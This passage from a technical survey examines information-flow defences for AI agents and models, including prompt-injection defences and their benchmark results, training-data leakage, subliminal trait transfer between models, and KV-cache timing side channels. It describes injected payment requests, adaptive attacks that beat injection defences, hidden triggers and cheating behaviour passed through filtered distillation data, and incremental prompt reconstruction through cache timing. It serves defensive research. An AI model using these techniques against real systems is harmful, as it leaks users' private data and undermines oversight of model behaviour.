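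| Agent and model | AgentDojo tasks | Completed without checks | Completed with checks | Successful attacks with checks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Single context, GPT-4o | All | 84.3% | 41.9% | 0 |
| FIDES, GPT-4o | All | 60.6% | 50.0% | 0 |
| CaMeL, GPT-5.2 | Banking | 66.7% | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |
| Randori, GPT-5.2 | Banking | Checks always on | 75.0% | 2 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement, Qwen3.7-plus | Banking | Checks always on | 62.5% | 0 of 432 |

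Randori, which appears to avoid the drawbacks of checking, is not entirely comparable with CaMeL because it enforces only some of CaMeL's policies and its planner may exempt data from them. Randori completed 75% of 16 tasks, with a margin of error of about 19 percentage points. With Qwen3.7-plus, it also completed 75%, but this fell to 62.5% without endorsement.

Most of the resistance to attack also comes from planning in advance. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack needs a tool call or file that would never appear in a plan for the user's task, so only the other 47 test the labels.

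### Approvals

A system that asks the user about every blocked call can complete more tasks, but Willison expected users to click "OK" as fast as possible. Kolluri and colleagues reply that labels reduce the number of questions, because an agent with labels needs to ask only when a call fails the policy, whereas many current agents ask before every action with lasting effects. They counted the approvals an agent needed over all the AgentDojo tasks it completed. With OpenAI's o3-mini, the average was 48.2 for an agent without labels, 32.4 for the same agent with labels, and 18.8 for FIDES.

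The agent Prudentia adds two features to FIDES. It gives the planner the policies, so that the planner can avoid calls that will fail, and it can ask the user to endorse data. If an email contains ten tasks, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten calls. With o4-mini, Prudentia needed 19.2 approvals and completed 73.2% of the tasks, while FIDES needed 36.8 and completed 75.7%. With o3-mini and no approvals, Prudentia completed 59.1%, compared with 50.1% for FIDES and 24.3% for the agent without labels.

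Prudentia was also tested on WASP, a benchmark in which an agent uses simulated websites. Attacks diverted the ordinary agent in 14.6% to 61.1% of cases, depending on the model and the website. None succeeded against Prudentia, which needed no approvals. But the tasks were easy for this design, because posting a comment or voting for a post doesn't require the planner to read what strangers have written.

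Fewer questions should make users less tired, but Kolluri and colleagues assumed that users would stop every harmful call and did not test whether they answer correctly. Endorsing an email is a bigger decision than approving a call, since one mistake lets the email influence everything the agent does afterwards. Kolluri and colleagues decided against a similar option for declassifying secrets because whether a secret should be released usually depends on who will receive it.

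Security also depends on exactly what the user approves. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) considers an agent that needs approval for each message. If the approval permits the next message, whatever it contains, an injected call can use it to send private data before the agent sends the user's reply. The agent then cannot send the reply because the approval has been used. If the user approves the exact text and recipient, only that message can go out. An attacker who can measure time may still learn whether the private data equals the approved reply, because an injected attempt to send the data succeeds only if the two match, and the reply then arrives one step early.

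### Leaks that the task already allows

Some agents violate noninterference by doing just what their users want. Dongol gives the example of an assistant that shares Alice's free times with anyone who asks for a meeting. Its replies depend on Alice's private calendar, so it violates noninterference even without an attack. Declassification can permit this release, but somebody has to write a suitable policy for every task.

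Dongol instead compares the agent with a reference agent. The reference agent follows the same plan, and the same monitor checks its calls, but its language model never obeys untrusted text. The real agent is relatively secure if an attacker who can use an injection to tell apart two possible values of the private data could also have told them apart through the reference agent. The idea comes from Spectre research, which compares a processor that executes instructions speculatively with one that does not. This definition allows an injection that makes the assistant send Alice's calendar, because a genuine meeting request would have revealed the same thing, but not one that makes it send a password reset code.

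Dongol proved that any agent with a fixed plan is relatively secure if, by the time it first reads untrusted text, the monitor has permanently withdrawn every tool that an injection could call. This holds however the agent's model interprets the text. The proof assumes that each injection causes a single tool call and that secrets do not affect when the model follows an injection. The attacker sees the contents and order of the messages that reach it, but not their timing.

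Withdrawing the tools later is not enough. If the agent reads an email, then a secret, and only then gives up its ability to send messages, an injected call can send the secret first. If the tools are withdrawn early, the agent can no longer reply to an email after reading it. The definition doesn't measure this loss of function, because the reference agent loses the same tools, and even a monitor that blocks every call satisfies it.

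### Wrong values in a permitted field

Both successful attacks on Randori involved the same task, in which the user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes. The attacker replaces the file with a different payment request, and the agent follows the user's instruction by making that payment. The planner has endorsed the file because the task is impossible otherwise, so withholding endorsement would block the genuine payment as well as the attack. According to Garby and colleagues, CaMeL's designers encountered the same case and placed it outside the attacks they aimed to stop.

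Labels record where an account number came from, but not whether it is the right one. A system that controls the route data takes must still decide which data to let through, as the censor does in Rushby's encryption device. A policy can refuse untrusted account numbers, accept only payees the user has paid before, or ask the user. Costa and colleagues describe a milder case, where an email makes the quarantined model return an empty summary. Requiring a trusted summary would prevent this, but would also rule out summarising emails from strangers.

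### Training models to resist injections

The main alternative is to train the language model to treat outside text as data, not instructions. Kolluri and colleagues mention several such methods, including instruction hierarchy, StruQ and SecAlign. Trained resistance needs no labels or per-tool policies, and it lets the planner read everything, so it avoids most of the task failures seen in label-based designs. Kolluri and colleagues acknowledge that label-based designs do worse on task completion, with losses of up to 30% on AgentDojo. A well-trained model might also detect a suspicious payment request, which labels cannot do.

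The case against relying on training is that attackers can keep trying. In 2025 Nasr and colleagues bypassed twelve defences against prompt injection and related attacks by adapting their attacks to each defence. According to Kolluri and colleagues, the attacks succeeded every time against a combination of StruQ and instruction hierarchy. Willison argues that stopping 99% of attacks is not good enough in security. If each attempt independently has a 1% chance of success, an attacker who sends 100 different emails has a probability of 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%, of succeeding at least once.

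Training could make the quarantined model less likely to return a wrong address or an empty summary, while the policy limits the damage when it does. Costa and colleagues also suggest that a system might relabel a document as trusted after a classifier finds no injection in it. This would let the agent complete more tasks, but any injection the classifier missed would be labeled trusted and pass every later check.

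## Training, weights and shared caches as channels

A partition around a model controls what the model can read and send while it runs. It does not control what data the model was trained on, or what the serving software beneath the model shares between customers. Information can cross between domains by either route without breaking any rule the kernel enforces.

*Information Flow Control in Machine Learning through Modular Model Architecture* (Tiwari, Gururangan and colleagues, 2023) gives the example of a company that trains a code-completion model on all its repositories, even though each engineer is allowed to read only some of them. Large models can reproduce parts of their training data, so the model may suggest code from a project the engineer is not allowed to see, even if the model runs in a partition that cannot reach any repository.

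Rushby's access tables depend on dividing a machine's state into named locations. A network's weights, the numerical parameters set during training, don't divide this way. Ordinary training can adjust any weight for any example, so a single weight mixes the influence of data from many owners. An access table could have only one entry for the whole file of weights, and anyone allowed to query the model can in effect observe the whole file.

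### Noninterference for training data

Tiwari and colleagues restated noninterference for this situation. The training data D consists of separate sets, one for each domain, and an access policy a lists the domains whose data a particular user may benefit from. Let M(D, a, x) be the probability distribution over the replies to a query x from a model trained on D. The model satisfies noninterference for a if, for every query x and any two collections D and D′ that contain the same data for all the domains in a:

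M(D, a, x) = M(D′, a, x)

For example, D′ could be D without one forbidden domain's data. Removing that data and retraining the model replaces the purge. If the probability of any reply changes, the forbidden data has interfered. Like Gray's condition, this test compares the probabilities of replies, not just which replies are possible. It also covers where a reply ends, since the reply's length could carry information.

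Testing cannot establish this condition, just as it cannot establish earlier forms of noninterference, and here each comparison needs another training run. Different random numbers also change the trained network, so the comparison has to keep them fixed or average over them. Designers therefore look for training methods that guarantee the condition.

The simplest way to keep restricted data from leaking through a model's weights is to train only on data that everybody may see, but the model then learns nothing from the restricted data. Tiwari and colleagues measured this loss with GPT-2, an early OpenAI model, on text from 50 Reddit communities that stood in for access-controlled domains. Average perplexity, a measure of how badly a model predicts text, was 55.5 for the public model and 29.8 for a copy trained further on all 50 communities. Training a separate model for every possible access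 policy would avoid the loss, but 50 domains allow 2⁵⁰ policies, more than a million billion.

### Differential privacy

Differential privacy limits the influence of training data instead of forbidding it. In the usual definition, a training method T is differentially private if, for any two datasets D and D′ that differ in one example, and for every set O of possible results:

P(T(D) ∈ O) ≤ e^ε × P(T(D′) ∈ O) + δ

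If ε and δ are both 0, the probabilities must be equal, so the example has no influence and the condition amounts to noninterference for it. If ε is 1 and δ is 0, including or omitting the example can make any result at most e¹ ≈ 2.72 times as likely. A positive δ allows a small further difference.

The table shows what this means when δ = 0 for an attacker who initially thinks there is a 50% chance that a particular document was in the training data.

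| ε | Largest ratio of probabilities | Attacker's greatest possible confidence afterwards |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 1 | 50% |
| 0.1 | 1.11 | 52.5% |
| 1 | 2.72 | 73.1% |
| 8 | 2,981 | 99.97% |

These are upper limits, and an actual attack may achieve much less. Still, the formal guarantee for ε = 8, which Tiwari and colleagues call moderate, rules out very little.

The guarantee also weakens when related examples must be protected together. With δ = 0, a method that gives ε for one example gives only kε for a group of k. The Reddit domains contained between 3,000 and 900,000 examples each, so ε = 8 per example becomes ε = 24,000 for even the smallest domain. Getting ε = 1 for that whole domain would require ε = 1/3,000 per example.

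Private training usually limits how much each example can change the weights and adds random noise, both of which make learning harder. Tiwari and colleagues cite studies in which private fine-tuning (further training) of the finished GPT-2 model reduced accuracy by 1% to 40% at ε = 8 per example. GPT-2 is an old model, so these figures are weak evidence of how much accuracy a current model would lose. *The Privacy-Hallucination Tradeoff in Differentially Private Language Models* (2026) considers a different drawback, an increase in false statements.

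Fine-tuning with differential privacy also leaves the original training data unprotected. *VaultGemma* (2025) describes a 1-billion-parameter Google model trained with differential privacy throughout. Its developers called it the largest openly available language model trained this way.

Differential privacy limits what anyone can learn from an example, including people cleared to see it. This suits data from millions of people who should not be able to read each other's contributions, but it suits the company's repositories less well because an engineer on a project should get the full benefit of that project's code. Tiwari and colleagues therefore defined a graded version of their condition, which applies the e^ε limit only to domains that the user may not access. They left designing a system that uses it to future work.

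### Separately trained experts

The system they built again gives each domain's information a known location in the weights. It starts with a model trained on public data and freezes its weights. For each domain, it adds a small set of new weights, called an expert, and trains the expert only on that domain's data. When a user sends a query, the system selects a few relevant experts from those the user may access and combines their predictions.

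Even when the experts are kept apart, the selection among them can leak information. If a selector has been trained on everyone's data, its choice among permitted experts may depend on forbidden data. Tiwari and colleagues therefore compare the start of the user's text only with summaries of each domain the user can access.

Tiwari and colleagues also offer a faster method for large numbers of domains, which groups similar domains in advance and searches only the closest group. It recalculates the centre of each group from permitted domains alone, but the grouping itself uses all domains. Changing a forbidden domain's data could therefore move a permitted domain to another group and affect which experts the system selects. This version appears to violate the strict definition, although they present it as secure.

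With all 50 Reddit domains accessible, the system reduced GPT-2's perplexity by about 38%, compared with 48% for a model fine-tuned on all the data without protection. With one accessible domain, the reduction was 11.5%. In tests on 79 code repositories, the system reduced perplexity by 44% to 62%, depending on the programming language, compared with about 75% without protection. It added at most 1.9% to response time, but had to run three experts in parallel on three graphics processors to do so. Merging the selected experts into one avoids the need for extra processors, but reduced perplexity on the Reddit data by only 29%.

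All users still share the original model, so the guarantee does not cover a confidential document that was already in its supposedly public training data.

Shi, Bhagia and colleagues (2025), in *FlexOlmo*, applied a similar idea to owners who will not hand over their data. Each owner receives a public model with 7 billion parameters and trains an expert on their own premises. A router later joins the experts into one model and decides which of them process each piece of text. During training, each expert works alongside a frozen copy of the public model, which makes it compatible with experts trained separately. When Shi and colleagues omitted this step in a test with four datasets, the average score fell from 46.7 to 38.8.

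With seven simulated private datasets, the combined model averaged 52.4 on 31 tasks, compared with 42.4 for the public model alone. That is an improvement of about 24%, although the paper's summary gives 41%. Separation reduced performance somewhat. In the smaller test, FlexOlmo scored 47.8, while a model trained on all four datasets together, using about twice as much computation, scored 51.5.

An owner can withdraw by removing their expert, and Shi and colleagues say that this completely removes the influence of their data. The claim seems to fail if training included an optional last stage, which adjusts the routing for all the experts together on public text chosen to resemble each private dataset. The routing for the remaining experts then retains some influence from the owner who left, unless somebody repeats that stage. Skipping the stage lowered the average score only from 52.4 to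 51.3, so strict removal need not lower performance much.

While an expert remains in the model, its training data can leak to anyone who uses the model. Shi and colleagues gave each model the first 32 tokens (words or pieces of words) of 10,000 mathematical documents and counted a document as extracted if any of ten continuations closely matched the original. They extracted 1.6% of the documents from the mathematics expert alone and 0.7% from the combined model. The rate was 0.1% for a public model that had never seen the documents, presumably because some continuations are predictable. They recommend differential privacy for experts trained on sensitive data.

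### Gradient routing

Separate experts require correctly sorted training data. If a confidential document is put in the public set by mistake, its influence spreads through the shared model. *Gradient Routing* (Cloud, Goldman-Wetzler and colleagues, 2024) presents a method that tolerates some of these mistakes but isolates data less strictly.

Each training step measures a network's error on some examples and computes a gradient, which shows how to change each weight to reduce that error. Gradient routing multiplies parts of the gradient by a mask that depends on the example, where 0 blocks a change and 1 permits it. The developer can therefore direct what the network learns from certain data into a chosen region and later delete that region.

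In a small demonstration, Cloud and colleagues used a network that compressed images of handwritten digits into 32 numbers and reconstructed the images from them. They routed the digits 0 to 4 to one half of these numbers and 5 to 9 to the other half. A second network, given only the half for 5 to 9, could reconstruct those digits but produced nearly the same image for every digit from 0 to 4.

They also trained a language model with 0.7 billion parameters and routed what it learned about 20 virology terms, such as "virus" and "vaccine", to a small region. They deleted the region, repaired the model with ordinary text, and then tried to restore the lost knowledge by training on two virology documents. The model's prediction error on virology text was still 0.182 higher than before the deletion, compared with 0.032 higher on ordinary text. Leaving the 20 terms out of the measurement made little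 difference, so the model had lost more than the terms themselves.

Cloud and colleagues call this broader effect absorption. Once a region has learned something useful from labelled data, it also helps with related unlabelled data, so training puts less pressure on the rest of the network to learn the same thing. In a test on children's stories, routing followed by deletion removed knowledge of forests better than leaving out the labelled stories when some forest stories were unlabelled, but it also made the model worse at other stories. *Beyond Data Filtering* (2025) presents an improved variant, which removed biology knowledge from a model trained on Wikipedia with less damage to other knowledge than filtering the articles.

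However, the whole network still helps compute every prediction during training, even when the mask blocks some weight updates. What the ordinary weights learn therefore depends on what the routed region has already learned, and deleting the region does not undo this. Gradient routing makes a capability harder to recover, but it does not provide noninterference for the data.

### Traits that pass through filtered data

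All these designs assume that one domain's training data contains nothing derived from another's. Distillation, the common practice of training one model on another's output, can break this assumption even when the output looks harmless. In 2025 Cloud and different co-authors reported an effect they named subliminal learning.

*Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact* (Nief, Fu and colleagues, 2026) describes an experiment in which a teacher model is instructed to love cats and then continues lists of random three-digit numbers. A program discards every reply that contains anything except correctly formatted numbers. A student model, which starts as a copy of the same original model without the instruction, trains on the remaining lists. When asked for its favourite animal, the student may then name cats much more often than before. According to *Slow Decay and Silenced Expression* (2026),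 the filter in the original number experiments discarded between 23% and 38% of the data, yet students still acquired the trait. They also acquired it from computer code and written reasoning.

A mathematical argument explains why it helps if both models start with the same weights. Suppose the teacher's weights differ from that starting point by a small change Δ. On the student's training prompts, the teacher's outputs then differ from the student's by about JΔ, where J is the matrix of derivatives of the outputs with respect to the weights. A training step that reduces the squared difference changes the student's weights by ηJᵀJΔ, where η is a small positive number. To find out whether this moves the student towards the teacher, take the product with Δ:

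Δ · ηJᵀJΔ = η‖JΔ‖² ≥ 0

The student therefore moves partly in the teacher's direction, whatever the prompts are about, unless the teacher's change has no effect on these outputs. *Quantum Subliminal Learning* (2026) points out that the original proof guarantees this only for the first step near the shared starting point, not for a whole training run.

Experiments have found several conditions under which the trait does not pass, or passes only weakly:

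- In the original study, a preference for owls did not pass from OpenAI's GPT-4.1 to Qwen, a model from Alibaba.
- Shuffling the numbers or paraphrasing the text destroys the signal, according to *Subliminal Learning is Non-Semantic Distillation* (2026).
- Nief and colleagues found the effect with LoRA, a cheap method that trains a small addition to the weights, but not when they trained all the weights. *Subliminal Learning Is Steering Vector Distillation* (2026) reports the same failure with full training in three models.
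- The effect often depends on the system prompt, the standing instructions at the start of a conversation. One of Nief and colleagues' students mentioned wolves in 50.4% of its replies under the prompt used in training, but in only 12.9% when they removed it.

Nief and colleagues conclude that subliminal learning is a fragile by-product of LoRA. They could not test this explanation on the OpenAI models in the original study because OpenAI does not publish how its fine-tuning service works. Their results also don't justify trusting a short test of the student, since a tester who uses a different system prompt might miss the trait.

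Later experiments transferred skills as well as preferences. In *Beyond Owls*, Dubiński, Sztyber-Betley and colleagues (2026) trained a teacher model to count letters, then trained a student model on the teacher's answers to 11,000 unrelated instructions. The student's letter-counting accuracy rose from 27.3% to 59.8%. In the first version of the experiment, which had a weaker effect, a control student trained on the original model's answers stayed at 26.6%.

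In another experiment, the teacher answered in French whenever a prompt contained a female name. A student trained only on data about number sequences answered in French for 23.5% of such prompts, and never for prompts with a male name or no name. A third student, trained on numbers from a teacher that cheated at chess, tried to cheat in 58.3% of games, compared with 10.9% for the untrained model.

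In the French and chess experiments, the student trained on the teacher's probabilities for the 32 most likely tokens at each position, which carry more information than the text alone. When Dubiński and colleagues tried to transfer knowledge of an arbitrary mathematical function, a student trained on such probabilities explained 38% of the variation in the function's output, compared with 92% for the teacher. A student trained only on the text explained none.

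A content filter between two models has the same weakness as the censor in Rushby's encryption device, since valid messages can still carry hidden data. Ten random three-digit numbers can carry almost 100 bits, so 10,000 such lists can carry about a million bits. The lists can carry hidden data without a deliberate message or any objectionable content, because the teacher model's weights affect which numbers it generates.

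Withholding the teacher's probabilities narrows the channel. Starting the student from a different model may block it, but this is not reliable by itself, because *Slow Decay and Silenced Expression* cites a study in which ordinary prose carried a trait between different model designs. *Defence against the dark arts of distillation* (2026) proposes a method that detects and prevents the transfer without making the student worse at its task. The method was tested on animal preferences, which transferred in all eight new training tasks, though not for every animal. These tests do not show that the method would stop a hidden trigger like the female names.

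The cautious rule is to give a model's output the combined label of everything that shaped the model, as information-flow control does for an agent's context. If a teacher model has learned from confidential data, filtering its output would not remove the label, because retraining the teacher without that data could change the numbers it generates, and therefore the weights of a student trained on them.

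### Caches shared between customers

The software that serves a language model can also create a channel between customers whose data was not used to train it. For each token the model reads, it calculates intermediate values, called keys and values, which it needs to process all later tokens. Servers store these in a KV cache and can reuse them to start replying sooner when another request begins with the same text.

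Prompt caching saves a lot of computation when many customers send the same long instructions or document, but it also creates a timing channel like those in processor caches. An attacker guesses how somebody else's prompt begins, sends that text, and measures how long the reply takes to start. A fast start suggests that the server has recently processed the same text.

The attacker can extend a correct guess a little at a time, which makes the search much easier. With a vocabulary of 50,000 tokens, a prompt of 20 tokens has 50,000²⁰ possible values. If the attacker can test each token separately, finding all 20 takes at most 20 × 50,000 = 1 million guesses, and far fewer if the attacker uses another language model to pick the most likely tokens to try first.

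*Governing the KV Cache* (2026) reports that three published attacks, PromptPeek, EarlyBird and InputSnatch, reconstructed victims' prompts with a 100% success rate. *Characterizing Contention-Induced Reliability Collapse in KV-Cache Timing Side Channels for Multi-Tenant LLM Serving* (2026) studies how competition for resources on a busy server can make an attacker's timing measurements less reliable. Repeating a measurement may let the attacker average out some of that noise, so a heavy load is not a dependable defence.

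The attacks work because the server looks up stored values by the text alone, no matter who sent it. The proposed fix, KVGov, adds a secret value for each customer to the lookup, so the same text leads to different entries for different customers and an attacker's guess cannot match a victim's entry. This divides the cache by customer, as cache colouring divides a processor's cache by partition.

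The simplest form of the fix prevents customers from reusing each other's cached computation. If 1,000 customers send the same 2,000-token document, the server has to process 2 million tokens instead of 2,000. *Selective KV-Cache Sharing to Mitigate Timing Side-Channels in LLM Inference* (2025) proposes sharing only some entries. KVGov has a variant meant to preserve reuse between customers, presumably by applying the secret value only to the private part of a prompt. Any such compromise depends on correctly identifying private text.

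Even with separate lookups, customers' cache entries may share the same memory. Heavy use by one customer can then push out another's entries, and the second customer will notice slower replies to its own repeated prompts. This reveals activity, not the text of a prompt, but two cooperating customers could use it to send messages, as High and Low did with the shared disk. The remedy is again a fixed memory quota for each customer.
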